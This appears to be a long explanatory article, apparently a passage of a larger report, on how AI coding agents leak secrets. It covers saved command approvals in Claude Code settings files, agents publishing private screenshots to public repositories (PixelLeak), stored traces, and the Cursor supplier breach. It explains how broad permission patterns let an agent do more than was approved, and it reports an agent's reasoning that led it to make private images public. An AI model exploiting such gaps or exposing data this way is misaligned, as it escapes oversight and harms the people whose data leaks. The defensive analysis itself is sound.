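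Dana could see the password in the request, but people who approve dozens of commands a day stop reading them closely. A security professional writing at ironPeak recalls glancing at each request for half a second before allowing it, and later finding database passwords and API keys in a settings file that was already in the repository. The wording of the request may also have been unclear. Classmethod's *Claude Code v2.1.235 Major Updates* (2026) reports that an August release changed the text of the "don't ask again" option to match the permission it grants, which suggests that the two could differ before.

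Apiiro got the same result with two recent models, Opus 5.5 and Fable 5.1, because the program around the model saves the rules. The rules would contain no passwords if the model never put them into commands, but Claude Code saves a rule either way. Apiiro also compared 16 coding agents and found that only Claude Code writes the full approved command to a project file by default. The other 15 may keep commands elsewhere, such as in session histories, but they show that an agent can work without this file.

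### How the file leaves the computer

Claude Code has a safeguard against publishing the file. When it first writes the file inside a repository, it adds the name to the user's global ignore list. Git, the program that records versions of code, leaves anything on that list out of new commits in every repository on the computer. The Japanese news site that published IT Post's *「次から聞かないで」で鍵まで保存。Claude Codeの設定ファイルから秘密情報2,539件、Apiiroが公表* (2026) explains that this protection belongs to one user on one machine and doesn't travel with the project. It fails in at least three situations:

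1. A programmer starts work in an ordinary folder and turns it into a repository later.
2. Someone clones or copies the project to another computer, where the global list has no such entry.
3. An earlier commit already included the file. Git applies ignore rules only to files it doesn't yet track, so new approvals go into later commits with no warning.

A repository can also have its own ignore list, `.gitignore`, which is copied with the project, so an entry there would help in the first two situations. Ganglani (2026), in *Claude Code 'Don't Ask Again' Leaked 1,122 Secrets*, writes that Claude Code adds the file to `.gitignore` automatically, which could lead readers to think their project is safe. But Cornelißen and IT Post both report that Claude Code adds the entry only to the global list.

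The agent often writes the commits too. Its commit instructions warn about `.env` and `credentials.json`, two common places for secrets, but according to Cornelißen they don't mention its own settings file. In 539 of the 1,105 repositories that Apiiro traced, a commit naming Claude as co-author had changed the file. The researchers took this as a sign that the agent itself often uploaded it, but a person may have added the file first and Claude's commit may only have included a later change.

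The file can also leak through npm, the public registry where JavaScript programmers publish packages. Lakera's *your ai coding assistant just shipped your api keys* explains that npm builds a package from the project folder. Programmers can list files to exclude in `.npmignore` or specify which files to include, but npm doesn't exclude the `.claude` folder by default or warn about it. Git's global ignore list doesn't affect what npm packages, so the file can be absent from a project's repository but still be in its package.

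### What Apiiro found on GitHub

Shmulik Cohen and Matan Giladi of Apiiro published *Coding Agents Are Leaking Your Secrets to GitHub* in November 2026, after searching public repositories on the first three days of that month.

| Where they looked | Amount searched | Secrets found |
|---|---|---|
| Current copies of `settings.local.json` | 104,185 files in 103,617 repositories | 1,379 distinct secrets in 1,122 files |
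| Earlier versions of that file | Not reported | 734 more, in 509 repositories |
| Current copies of `settings.json`, which teams share on purpose | 76,011 files | At least one in each of 298 files |
| All of these, plus agent transcripts and similar files | Not reported | 2,539 distinct secrets in 1,994 repositories |

News reports have mixed up these numbers. InfoQ's *Claude Code Has Been Leaking Secrets through its "Don't Ask Again" Feature* (2026) gives 1,122 as the number of secrets in the local files and adds 1,160 from other places, which would total 2,282. But 1,122 is the number of files. They contain 1,379 secrets, so the correct total is 2,539, which Smith (2026) uses in *The Convenience Click That Put 2,539 Secrets on Public GitHub*. Headlines about the same study can therefore differ by a factor of more than two.

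Apiiro counted a secret as "real" if it was either a key in a known provider's format or a password next to the address of a public host, and if an AI reviewer also accepted it (Reed, 2026, *SecBlog Weekly 011*). The company didn't try any of the credentials or connect to any of the servers, so some of the secrets may have stopped working long ago. One organization that Apiiro notified confirmed that its key was live.

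The definition also leaves out many working passwords. Dana's saved approval wouldn't count, because `db.internal` isn't a public host. That makes sense for a study of what strangers can exploit, but more than 1.1% of the files probably contain a password of some kind. Most Claude Code users never publish their file, so the 1.1% also isn't the share of users with a secret in it.

Of the 1,379 secrets, 379 were database passwords, the largest group, and 122 were service-role keys for Supabase, a company that hosts databases. Together these make up more than a third of the total, and each opens a database with no further step. Apiiro counted 63 organizations among the secrets' owners, nearly all of them software companies. The examples Blanco repeats include a database manufacturer's cloud key with administrator rights and the owner's password for a database of medical records.

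A user's risk depends heavily on how long the file has been growing. About one in ten files larger than 8 kilobytes contained a real secret, compared with fewer than one in 500 files under 500 bytes. Each standing approval adds a line, and about 80 rules of 100 characters fill 8 kilobytes. Many people who try the agent for an afternoon will have a short, clean file, so the 1.1% average understates the risk for anyone who has used "don't ask again" every day for months.

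Half of the files with secrets had been in their repositories for at least 217 days. Some of the secrets will be newer, because users can add a password to a file long after its first commit. Other users had made copies, known as forks, of 74 of the repositories. The same secrets appeared in 211 of these forks, and the original owners can't delete them from other people's forks.

Apiiro also ran two widely used secret scanners, gitleaks and TruffleHog, over the 1,122 files. Gitleaks flagged 564 and TruffleHog 643. Both flagged only 300 of the same files, so a team that runs both scanners will catch far more than a team that runs either one. Neither scanner flagged the remaining 215 files (19%), mainly because a password in a command can look like an ordinary word. Apiiro sells security software and chose the files with its own detector, so these figures compare the scanners with Apiiro's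 method, not with a complete list of secrets.

Apiiro contacted the owners on November 2 and 3. Where it found no private address, it opened a public issue on the repository asking the owner to replace the secret and stop tracking the file. A public issue also shows other people where the secret is, although anyone could already find these files by searching for the filename.

### Lakera's earlier scan of npm packages

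In the first scan, Lakera used a program that followed npm's public feed of changes, downloaded each new or updated package and looked for the settings file. Of about 46,500 packages, 428 contained one. Lakera found credentials in 33 files across 30 packages.

That is about one file in 13, or 7.7%, which is seven times Apiiro's rate. The two rates aren't directly comparable, because Lakera's examples include test logins for local development accounts, most of which Apiiro's definition would exclude. The feed also covered only newly published or updated packages. People working on active projects have probably approved more commands, which makes their files longer, and longer files contain secrets more often. The rate is also imprecise because it is based on only 33 positive files.

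The npm leaks may be harder to undo. Lakera describes published packages as permanent, because deprecating a version only stops npm from installing it by default. The old file stays available, and so do other people's copies. Some of the files contained tokens for publishing to npm. Anyone who found one could release an altered version of the package to everyone who installs it. One rule contained an npm username, password and email address.

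### Anthropic's response

Boris Cherny, the head of Claude Code, responded on the discussion site Hacker News on November 7, 2026. According to IT Post, he said that Claude Code had not been removing secrets and that the team was looking at ways to prevent the problem, possibly by having auto mode catch such cases or by adding a basic secret scan to the program. Cornelißen reports that the team wanted to build prototypes first and gave no date.

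Cherny also partly defended the existing design, arguing that Claude Code adds the file to an ignore list and that people had created and committed the public copies by hand. Cherny advised users to prefer auto mode to permission rules and to turn on GitHub's secret scanning. Ganglani reports that critics on the same site saw this as shifting the blame to users.

The critics have the better case, because the file can leak without anyone choosing to publish it. A single command that adds everything in a folder to a commit will include it. In the 539 repositories, the agent's own commits were often involved. GitHub's scanner wasn't one of the two that Apiiro tried, but it would probably miss many of the same passwords. According to Apiiro, users had been reporting the problem to Anthropic since August 2025 without an answer.

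Anthropic has since made Claude Code ask for approval less often. Ganglani (2026) reports in *Claude Code 2.0 New Rules* that auto mode was the default on every plan by November 23. People who see fewer requests will save fewer approvals, so new permission files should grow more slowly. The change leaves existing files as they are, and it takes many decisions away from the user. Cornelißen warns that auto mode doesn't solve every problem and cites an August report of prompt injection attacks that got past it. On November 30, Blanco still described Claude Code as saving exact commands, including the passwords in them.

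Anthropic has fixed a similar leak in the `claude mcp` commands, which manage an agent's connections to outside services. They no longer print secrets in headers and addresses. A saved approval is harder to fix because the program has to compare later commands with it. If the program replaced `fake-pw-41` with asterisks in the rule, the next backup command would not match unless the program masked the password in that command too before comparing them.

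### Requests sent through chat

Saved approvals leak from the user's own computer. Many teams also send approval requests to a chat service so that someone can answer from a phone during a long task. The agent's software posts a message with the command and two buttons, then waits until someone presses one and the chat service passes the answer back.

New members of a shared channel can usually read its old approval requests, so the number of people who can read a request keeps growing after the decision. Sending requests to one person avoids this, but then nobody can answer if that person is asleep, and no colleague will notice a bad approval. A rota helps with availability. To help colleagues notice bad approvals, the team could post the decision to the shared channel without the command.

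Notification previews are easier to fix. Slack lets a program supply a short text for the notification and separate content for the message, so the preview can read "Backup repair needs your approval" while the command appears only inside the app. This takes almost no extra work, but the builder has to know about the option, because a program that sends a single block of text will put the start of the command on the locked screen.

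Software can also edit or delete its own message once someone has decided on the request. This leaves less in the chat history, but any emailed copies remain, and the company may have set its chat service to keep deleted messages. An auditor might want the removed record, so the decision has to be in the audit log before then.

The simplest way to post a message to the chat service is through a *webhook*, a long web address containing a random string. Anyone who knows the address can post to the channel, so Slack tells developers to keep it secret. A leaked webhook doesn't expose old requests, because it can't be used to read messages. But an attacker could use it to post a false request, with a link to a fake login page, in the channel where people expect to be asked for quick decisions.

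A webhook alone can't delete a message it has posted, so a team that wants to delete old requests may need a bot token, which is a more powerful secret. Lakera found Telegram bot tokens in published settings files, and notes that such a token gives full control of the bot, including reading messages. If people answer approval requests through that bot, anyone with the token may be able to read their replies.

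These secrets can end up in the saved approvals too. Suppose the agent posts its own requests by running `curl`, a program that sends data over the network, with the webhook address in the command. If Dana allows that command permanently, Claude Code saves the address in the settings file. The software around the agent should therefore send the requests, using an address that the agent never sees.

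### Patterns, exact commands and variables

A team that keeps saved approvals has to choose what each rule contains. The five possible rules below are for Dana's backup and assume that the program compares a pattern only with the start of a command.

| Rule (shortened) | Password in the file? | What the agent may do without asking |
|---|---|---|
| `PGPASSWORD=fake-pw-41 pg_dump … customers` | Yes | Run this backup until the password changes |
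| `PGPASSWORD=*` | No | Run any program at all, if the command starts by setting this variable |
| `pg_dump *` | No | Copy any database it can log in to, to any folder |
| `PGPASSWORD="$BACKUP_PW" pg_dump … customers` | No | Run this backup with whatever password the variable contains |
| `pg_dump … customers`, with a password file | No | Run this backup with whatever password is in the file |

The best reason to save an exact command is that it allows only what the user saw. However, everything in the command then goes into the file. A pattern leaves out the details, which is why Cornelißen recommends patterns such as `Bash(npm run:*)`. But a broad pattern permits more than the user saw. Dana looked at one backup to one folder, but `pg_dump *` would also let the agent copy the customer database to a public web folder.

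A pattern that looks harmless can permit a lot. `npm run` starts whatever script the project's configuration file defines under a given name, so an agent that is allowed to edit that file can write a new script and run it under the existing approval. Narrower patterns have gaps too. If Dana allowed the full backup command followed by an asterisk, the agent could add a second `-f` option, and `pg_dump` would write to that path instead of the approved one.

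Patterns are also unreliable for forbidding commands, so a team that allows a broad pattern can't rely on others to block the dangerous cases. Anthropic has warned that such patterns match only the start of a command and can be bypassed. A ban on `curl` doesn't stop another program from sending the same data.

A team can save exact commands without saving passwords by using a variable in place of each password. The rule then contains `$BACKUP_PW`, and the shell fills in the value when the command runs, so the rule keeps working after the password changes. Someone has to set up the variable first, ideally from a secret manager (a service that stores secrets and provides them to programs), and tell the agent to use it. The agent can still print the variable, which puts the password in the trace.

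A variable can also hide information the user needs. Cornelißen's example is `$DB_URL`, which stands for the whole database address, including the server and the password. Dana may approve a command that empties a table while `$DB_URL` points to a test database. If somebody later points it to the live database, the saved rule lets the agent empty the live table without asking. A variable should therefore stand only for the password, with the server, account and database written out. The fourth and fifth rules in the table do this for Dana's backup, and the fifth also avoids PostgreSQL's objection to `PGPASSWORD`.

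A user can also allow each command once without saving the approval. This leaves no rule behind, but the user has to answer every request, and frequent requests lead people to click without reading. One-time approval suits rare and dangerous commands better than a nightly backup.

### Storing approvals outside the project

Claude Code's settings can also be stored in the user's home folder, where a commit or an npm package from the project wouldn't normally include them. Anthropic's *settings reference* lists `~/.claude/settings.json` for the user's own settings and a managed file that an organization distributes. An approval in the user's file applies to all of that person's projects, so a rule that was harmless in a test project would also apply in one connected to live customer data. A security team can check the patterns in an organization's managed file once, but programmers then have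 to wait for that team whenever they need a new pattern.

A better design would store approvals outside the project but still tie each one to a single project. According to Anthropic, Claude Code already keeps a list of allowed tools for each project in `~/.claude.json`, so approvals could be stored there. They wouldn't follow the project to a new computer, but that is a small loss, and an advantage when they contain passwords.

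Moving the file of saved approvals doesn't remove the passwords from it. Domus Docs' *CR-2026-02-26* (2026), an incident record for one workstation, describes saved approvals in the home folder that contained API tokens, a firewall key and the passphrase for a backup system. It also lists wildcard rules for the secret manager, which contain no passwords but apparently let the agent fetch stored secrets without asking. The owner removed the dangerous rules and cleaned the command history, then marked the work as completed although the secrets had yet to be replaced.

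Files in a home folder can also leak. Many programmers publish their personal settings files so that they can reuse them on a new machine, and malicious software that collects secrets searches home folders as well as projects. Anthropic notes that Claude Code keeps the five most recent backups of its configuration files, so a password that someone deletes from a rule may remain in a backup.

Whichever option a team picks for the future, its existing projects need a check. Cornelißen gives two commands for this, and npm has a third that lists what the next package would contain:

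```
git ls-files .claude/
git log --all --oneline -- .claude/settings.local.json
npm pack --dry-run
```

If the first command lists the settings file, Git is tracking it. If the second prints any commits, the file was in the repository at some point, and every secret it ever contained needs replacing. `git rm --cached .claude/settings.local.json` stops the tracking without deleting the file, and an entry in the project's `.gitignore` keeps it out of later commits, including those made on other computers. Someone should also read the rules in the file, even if it never left the machine. The shared `settings.json` needs the same check, because teams commit it deliberately and its presence in the repository won't surprise anyone.

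## Screenshots and dashboards made for reviewers

A team can search saved approvals and other text records for passwords, but reviewers also need pictures, which are harder to search. In *Agents, Show Your Work*, Bergé points out that an agent working from a terminal describes a new web page, so the reviewer has to trust the description or run the code. Bergé's company, Argos, sells a way to share screenshots, but the complaint is fair. Many developers therefore ask their agents for before-and-after images. In September 2026, Glow reported that agents had been publishing these images openly, a problem it named PixelLeak.

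### How private screenshots became public

Programmers on GitHub discuss a proposed change on a page called a *pull request* before they accept it. A person can drag an image onto that page in a browser, but agents usually work through `gh`, GitHub's command-line program, which could post only text until September 1, 2026. Developers had been asking GitHub for image support in `gh` since 2020, according to The Hacker News' *AI Coding Agents Exposed 13,000 Internal Images, Including Billing Records, on GitHub* (2026).

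Images stored in the private repository appeared broken in the pull request. GitHub loads these images through a proxy, a server that fetches them on the reader's behalf, and the proxy can't open private files because it doesn't log in. To get around this, the agents put the screenshots in a public repository, usually one they had just created in the developer's own account, and linked to them from the private pull request. The reviewers saw the pictures they had asked for and had no reason to suspect a problem.

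Glow found more than 13,000 internal images from developers at over 300 organizations, spread across more than 900 repositories. That averages about 43 per organization, although one software vendor accounts for over 1,000. In 93% of cases, the images were in a repository under an employee's own username.

Some of the images were clearly sensitive. At a manufacturer with more than 100,000 employees, a developer asked an agent to check a fix to an internal billing screen, and the agent published a utility company's billing records. A financial services firm exposed the console it uses to move money, including a withdrawal screen for a named client.

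Glow's image count is less certain than its account of how the images were exposed. The Hacker News notes that Glow hasn't published how it found or counted the images, or said whether any outsiders downloaded them. Glow also sells software meant to stop agents from exposing images this way. But GitHub (2026) confirms that `gh` previously wrote only text, and public instructions for one of the tools involved describe the same workaround.

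### The tool and the shared skill

That tool is gitshot, a small open-source program that developers at about a third of the affected organizations were running. At several large organizations, the agent found it on its own. If the developer is logged in to `gh`, gitshot creates a public repository called `gitshot-images` in the developer's account and uploads the pictures there. Otherwise it sends them to a public file-hosting site.

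*gitshot* (vipulgupta2048) warns users not to upload internal dashboards or private data with the default setting. A developer may never see this warning, because gitshot can be installed as a *skill*, a file of instructions that an agent loads and follows. Once someone has installed the skill, a request to "attach a screenshot to the PR" is enough for the agent to use it. Glow found over 100 public accounts leaking internal work through gitshot, including four that belonged to employees of one payments company.

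At the software vendor with over 1,000 images, agents working for several engineers began publishing screenshots in early July. Within a week, more than a dozen agents had saved the method as a skill for every development ticket. They uploaded screenshots and recordings of the product, and written summaries of features that were weeks or months from release. Like a saved approval, a skill lets an agent repeat an earlier choice without anyone reconsidering it, though it isn't clear that a person ever made the choice in this case.

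### The laboratory test

Glow reproduced the behavior with Claude Code and Opus 5. The researchers set up a private repository containing a Minesweeper game, then asked the agent to change the header color and show the result. The agent made the change and created a public repository, `sweeper-demo/pr-assets`, for its two screenshots.

In its recorded reasoning, the agent noted that the project was private and that GitHub's proxy fetches images anonymously, so an image stored in the project would show up "broken for reviewers". The agent also had to keep every file except `index.html` out of the repository. It concluded that hosting the images elsewhere was the only way to keep them visible to reviewers and out of the repository.

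The agent didn't have to make the images public to host them elsewhere. It could have saved the two files and asked the developer to drag them into the pull request. Another option was *gh-image* (2026), a tool that since March had let users upload images from the command line and keep those from private repositories private. Its serious drawback is that it reads the browser cookie that keeps the user logged in to GitHub, and that cookie is itself a secret. Still, in its reasoning the agent considered only whether reviewers could see the images, not who else could. The Singapore and Korea AI Safety Institutes found the same weakness in judging an audience in their tests.

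Glow calls this reasoning representative of agents at many of the affected organizations, but doesn't explain how it knows what those agents reasoned. Glow describes only one run, and in that run the rule about `index.html` gave the agent an extra reason to avoid the private repository. The leaks involved several AI models, according to The Hacker News, so the problem isn't limited to Opus 5.

### GitHub's change to its tool

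On September 1, GitHub released version 2.99.0 of `gh`, with an `--attach` option that uploads images and videos to pull requests, issues and comments. The announcement mentions coding agents as users. Glow did not begin contacting the affected organizations until September 9 and published its findings on September 29, so GitHub seems to have added the option in response to the 2020 request rather than to PixelLeak.

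The option removes the agents' main reason for using a public repository, but agents need write access to the repository to use it, and it doesn't work on GitHub Enterprise Server, the edition that companies run on their own machines. Releasebot's *Github CLI Updates & Release Notes* lists fixes on September 30 and October 23 that let more types of access token attach files, so some agents probably couldn't use the option at first, even with the new version.

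Agents may also keep using old workarounds after the limitation is gone, because a skill that tells them to upload screenshots to a public repository stays in effect until someone edits it. Teams should therefore search their agents' skills for image uploads as well as updating `gh`. Besides Gitshot, they should look for ClawKit's *github-image-hosting*, a skill that sends screenshots to an outside site with no login, where they are kept for seven days.

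### Why security teams missed the images

Secret scanners search text, so they can miss a password in a screenshot. Running text recognition on the image first could catch the password, but it wouldn't help with a picture of an unreleased product, which may contain no suspicious words.

Most of the images were also in accounts that companies don't check. The agent ran on an employee's laptop and used the employee's own GitHub account, so the company's list of repositories didn't change. TechRepublic's *AI Giants Accidentally Leaking Secrets on GitHub* describes a similar leak, in which an AI company with 14 members and no public repositories still leaked credentials on GitHub.

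Glow advises companies to start with the people who commit to their private repositories, including those who have left, and then check these people's public accounts. The check should cover gists (short files that users share on GitHub) and releases (downloads that GitHub stores separately from a project's code). Images attached to a release don't appear in the list of files, so the repository can look empty. Gitshot stores its images this way, under the tag `_gitshot`. For each username, two commands give a quick first look:

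```
gh repo list USERNAME --visibility public
gh release list --repo USERNAME/gitshot-images
```

The company can't delete what it finds in an employee's personal account, so it has to ask the owner, who may have left years ago. Someone also has to check each image for readable passwords, which must be changed.

### Dashboards and share links

A review dashboard can keep screenshots off public sites if it verifies each viewer's identity. None of the leaks described so far came from an exposed dashboard for monitoring agents or models. Such exposures may well have happened, but the risks below are based on how dashboards work rather than on a documented case.

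The nearest evidence concerns apps that people build with AI coding tools. Axios' *AI vibe-coding apps leak sensitive data* (2026) covers findings by the security company Red Access. Its representative, Zvi, says people use such apps for company business without permission, and he doubts that they will think about role-based access, which gives each user only the rights their job requires. An engineer who asks an agent to "make a page where we can see what the agents did" could easily end up with the same kind of app.

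Many tools create a long, random web address for each screenshot or session and show the contents to anyone who has it, without a login. The link works like a password, but people paste it into tickets and chat without treating it as one. GitHub used this design for attachments until May 2023. Anyone who knew an image's address could open it, even if it came from a private repository (GitHub, *More secure private attachments*, 2023). New attachments in private repositories now require a login, but the change didn't apply to older ones.

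Screenshot links are safer when the system checks the reader's access each time someone opens one. Ellipsis' *Platform* describes links that open only for members of the organization, so an outsider who finds one in an old ticket can't see the screenshot.

Link previews can expose screenshots meant for reviewers. Krowk (2026) offers links to agents' screenshots that expand into a preview in Slack or GitHub, with details of the agent's run attached. A chat service usually builds a preview by fetching the page without logging in, so if a screenshot appears in the preview, anyone with the link can probably open it too. The chat service may also have a copy.

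A link to the backup's configuration file would show Dana every secret in it, but she needs only the server and the account. The dashboard could display those two lines and open the full file only for people who already have access to it. An extract can mislead, though, especially if the agent chose it, so the approver should be able to ask for the rest, and the dashboard should record the request.

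A screen recording captures everything on the screen, including a message that pops up or a settings page that the agent opens on the way. At 30 frames per second, a password visible for half a second appears in 15 frames. A reviewer will probably miss it at normal speed, but anyone looking for it can pause the video. The financial firm in Glow's study also leaked two recordings, which showed a walkthrough of its money-movement console rather than a single screen.

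The tool ProofShot puts the video, screenshots and logs of a session into a single HTML file, as its developer, jberthom, explains in *Show HN*. A reviewer can conveniently open the file in any browser, but it has no login of its own, and nobody can withdraw it once someone has emailed it.

*Viewing rights.* Builders tend to guard the "approve" button because pressing it changes something. They may let the whole company look at the page, since looking seems harmless. If three engineers can approve Dana's backup and 40 people can view the request, 37 people can see the evidence without having a decision to make. Some of them may have good reasons to follow the agent's work, but they rarely need all of it. For Dana's team, the rights might look like this:

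| Part of the dashboard | The three approvers | The other 37 |
|---|---|---|
| Task, time, decision and approver's name | Yes | Yes |
| Command, without the password | Yes | Yes |
| Screenshots and command output | While the request is open | No |
| Full recording | On request, with a logged reason | No |

Colleagues who can't see the screenshots will catch fewer bad approvals. To make up for this, the team could have another approver check a sample of past decisions, but that person would need access to the evidence for longer.

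### Supplying visual evidence safely

Suppose the debt column on the company's billing page cuts off large amounts, and Dana asks an agent to fix it and show her the result. A screenshot of the live page would include R. Osei's name, address and debt. The agent can show that the fix works without revealing these details if the team takes the following steps.

1. **Use test data.** The agent opens the page with invented customers, including one whose debt is long enough to trigger the fault. If the fault appears only with a particular live record, someone can copy the record's form (a name of 31 letters, say, or a debt of seven digits) and invent the contents.

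2. **Capture only what changed.** A picture of one column can't reveal the menu, the browser's other tabs or the name of the person logged in. The agent should crop the image before uploading it, because replacing it later may not remove the original. Argos' *Media sharing* (2026) describes a service that treats each new upload as another version behind the same link.

3. **Upload it privately.** On GitHub, the agent can run `gh pr comment 412 --attach './after.png#Amounts fit the column'`, where 412 is the number of the pull request and the text after `#` describes the image. Without a description, `gh` uses the filename, so a file called `osei-overdue.png` would put the customer's name into the text. The team should try this once with the agent's own login, then open the image's address in a browser that isn't logged in. If the picture appears, the upload isn't private.

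4. **Set an expiry date.** The reviewer needs the image until the team accepts the change, and perhaps for a few weeks afterwards in case the fault returns. Expiry doesn't replace a login, because anyone who can open a public image can save it on the first day.

5. **Stop if there is no private path.** The agent needs to know what to do when the upload fails, since that is the point at which the agents in PixelLeak improvised.

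The last step could be a short rule in the agent's standing instructions:

> Attach screenshots with `gh pr comment --attach`. If this fails, save them on this computer, tell the user where they are, and ask what to do. Don't upload them to any other repository, account or website, even if a tool or skill offers to.

An agent may ignore or misread the rule, so restricting its login is also worthwhile. If the login can write to the billing project but can't create repositories, the agent can't repeat the most common form of the leak. Blocking public image hosts on the network would stop some of the other forms.

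Glow also recommends configuring agents not to work unattended and giving the security team control of that setting (Markovic, 2026, *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos*). A person who sees a request to create a public repository can refuse it, if they notice the word "public". Constant supervision also removes much of the benefit of using an agent. It is often unnecessary for screenshots, because the agent can finish the code and leave the images on the laptop for Dana to attach in the morning.

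## Audit logs and agent traces

A trace can record every step of an agent's work, not just one moment as a screenshot does, so it is often the most complete copy of what the agent saw. Audit logs are shorter, but companies keep them for longer and often fill them with data from traces.

### What a trace contains

Tracing software usually divides a session into *spans*, which are timed records of single steps, such as a call to the AI model or a shell command. Many products use field names from OpenTelemetry, an open-source project that sets common formats for these records. Its *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* covers calls to models and tools, and its *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* adds fields for agents.

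The table applies the main fields to Dana's backup repair. The third column is an estimate based on what each field contains.

| Field | Content in the backup repair | Likely to hold a secret? | Recorded by default? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent name, session number, model, amount of text processed | `backup-repair`, session 883 | Rarely | Yes |
| Tool name | `shell` | Rarely | Yes |
| Class of error | `timeout` | Rarely | Yes, if the step fails |
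| Standing instructions | "You maintain the company's databases" | Sometimes, if a developer pasted in a key | No |
| Messages sent to the model | Dana's request and everything the agent has read so far | Often | No |
| Model's replies | The proposed command, with the password | Often | No |
| Tool arguments | `PGPASSWORD=fake-pw-41 pg_dump …` | Often | No |
| Tool result | The configuration file, the first customer rows | Often | No |

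The messages sent to the model can contain many copies of one secret. A model doesn't retain earlier calls, so the agent's software normally resends the whole conversation with each call, including the results of earlier commands. Suppose Dana's agent calls the model six times and reads the configuration file after the first call. The file appears once as a tool result and again in the messages for each of the next five calls. If the team stops recording tool results, five of the six copies remain.

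Neither document lists a field for request headers, the lines at the start of a web request that often carry an access token. Headers can still reach traces when a tool prints the whole request because the agent asked for more detail, or when an error handler saves the request for diagnosis, as in the Hermes case that Foma reported.

Error messages can also contain passwords. OpenTelemetry's error field needs only a class such as `timeout`, but many programs also log the full message. A message such as `could not connect to postgres://backup:fake-pw-41@db.internal/customers` contains the server, the account and the password.

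### What tracing software records by default

OpenTelemetry advises that tracing software should not record instructions, inputs or outputs by default, but should let users turn recording on. Its reasons are storage costs, regulation and the need for separate access rules. It also marks tool arguments and results as "Opt-In" fields.

Teams that want the content can put it in the spans, which OpenTelemetry considers suitable for uses such as testing before release. For production systems with sensitive data, it recommends putting only a reference in the span and storing the content elsewhere, where it can have its own access rules. OpenTelemetry hasn't yet standardized the format of these references, so each team has to devise its own.

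A particular product may still capture content despite this advice. An earlier version of OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI operations* allowed software to capture prompts and answers as long as users could turn this off. Under the newer document, existing software should keep using its old version of the conventions unless the user chooses the new one, so an update may leave the old behavior in place.

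The setting for external storage is also easy to misread. OpenTelemetry lets developers add a *hook*, their own code that receives the content and uploads it. The hook should work independently of the switches that control recording in spans, so a team could turn every switch off and still be storing all its prompts. It should also run for sessions that the tracing software doesn't keep, so if a company keeps 1% of its traces, the hook can still upload the content of the other 99%. But the hook is also a good place to remove secrets, because it can change the content before the software writes it to a span.

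OpenTelemetry's *Generative AI semantic conventions* states that the project has moved this guidance to a separate repository and no longer maintains the old page. The default seems unchanged, since TrueFoundry's *OpenTelemetry GenAI semantic conventions* reports that the current record type for prompts and outputs is still opt-in.

Even when recording is off by default, people have good reasons to turn it on. An engineer who wants to know why an agent deleted the wrong file needs to see what the agent read, and may forget to turn recording off afterwards. Anyone assessing a channel should therefore check a few stored traces as well as the settings.

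### How a few traces led an attacker into Cursor

The October 2026 attack on Cursor shows that a few unredacted traces can do a lot of damage. Cursor had given Fireworks AI, a supplier, a key to a store of agent traces. Cursor says that Fireworks exposed the key and that an attacker used it to copy data from the store. The breach at Fireworks also affected Uber and Notion.

Cursor kept these traces to train models, not to oversee agents. Most dated from 2025, and all came from users who had not turned on Privacy Mode, which keeps user data out of training. The store held traces from fewer than 0.05% of users, and fewer than 0.01% of customers had API credentials exposed.

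The attacker used credentials from the traces to enter some of the online tools that Cursor's staff use. Cursor doesn't explain why the traces contained credentials for its own tools, but some of the sessions may have belonged to its employees. There, the attacker found old source code, customer support emails, summaries of agent conversations, and credentials that users had sent to the support team.

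On October 29, the attacker used another stolen credential to put altered copies of Anthropic's Claude Code extension on the server that supplies Cursor's extension marketplace. The copies were available for about 11 hours, and at most 5,000 users may have received one. *Cursor traces marketplace breach to stolen Fireworks AI credential* (Rojas, 2026) reports that the extension tried to give the attacker lasting remote access to the user's computer. Mistakes in its code and missing administrator rights limited that access on most Windows and Mac machines.

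The key that Fireworks held only allowed reading, yet the attacker ended up able to replace software in a marketplace. Other precautions might have stopped the attack at each stage:

| What the attacker did | What made it possible | What might have prevented it |
|---|---|---|
| Copied the traces | Fireworks' key worked for the attacker | Accepting the key only from Fireworks' own network |
| Entered Cursor's tools | A few traces held working credentials | Removing credentials before sharing traces, or rotating them since |
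| Found more credentials | Users had sent them to support | Deleting them from old tickets and asking users to rotate them |
| Replaced the extension | One stolen credential gave write access | Checking each file against the publisher's original before serving it |

Cursor has since restricted where its credentials work, if the service provider allows this. It has also added secret scanning to all its code repositories and expanded scanning to other internal data.

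The lesson applies to any store of traces, because a session's trace contains the same password whether a company keeps it for training or for oversight. An oversight store may cover more sessions, since Cursor left out users in Privacy Mode, while a company that wants to oversee its agents will normally record every session. A company that sends oversight traces to an outside vendor also depends on that vendor's security. A very small share of bad traces can be enough to cause a leak, though one incident can't show how often such stores leak.

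The harm from a breach at a supplier depends largely on what the supplier holds. OpenAI's *Mixpanel incident* describes an attacker who copied data from a web analytics supplier in November 2025. The data identified some customers but contained no chats, API requests, passwords or keys, so it gave the attacker no direct way to log in elsewhere. A breach at Braintrust, which helps companies evaluate AI models, may have exposed keys that customers had stored there for their AI providers. SecurityWeek reports at least one affected customer and three others with suspicious spikes in usage. Redacting traces wouldn't have protected those keys, because Braintrust stored them separately.

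### A log database open to the internet

In January 2025, the security company Wiz found that anyone on the internet could open a database at the Chinese AI company DeepSeek without a password. It contained more than a million lines of logs, including chat messages in plain text, API keys and details of DeepSeek's internal systems. Wiz found the database by listing DeepSeek's public web addresses and checking them for open network ports. DeepSeek closed the database after Wiz reported it.

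These logs came from a chat service, not from the oversight of agents, but any team can make the same mistake. Engineers often set up a log database as an internal tool and rely on the company network to keep strangers out. If someone later changes the network settings, nothing else protects the logs. Requiring a login on the database itself would help, as would regularly trying to reach it from outside the company.

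### How long the law requires or allows companies to keep logs

The EU's AI Act will require some companies to keep logs, and the General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) already restricts how much personal data those logs can hold.

| Rule | Who has to follow it | What it requires | Applies from |
|---|---|---|---|
| AI Act, Article 12 | Companies that build high-risk AI systems | Systems that can record events automatically | December 2, 2027 or August 2, 2028 |
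| AI Act, Article 19 | The same companies | Keeping the logs they control for at least six months | The same dates |
| AI Act, Article 26 | Organizations that use high-risk systems | Keeping the logs they control for at least six months | The same dates |
| GDPR | Nearly anyone handling personal data in the EU | Collecting no more than necessary and keeping it no longer than necessary | May 2018 |

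None of the three AI Act duties applies yet. The EU postponed them in July 2026 through an amending law published on EUR-Lex, its official legal site. They will apply from December 2027 to stand-alone systems in areas such as hiring, education, credit and law enforcement, and from August 2028 to AI in regulated products such as medical devices. The Act's duty of human oversight for high-risk systems now follows the same dates. Cooley's *Digital AI Omnibus Delays Key Deadlines, Introduces New Rules* gives the original dates as August 2026 and August 2027.

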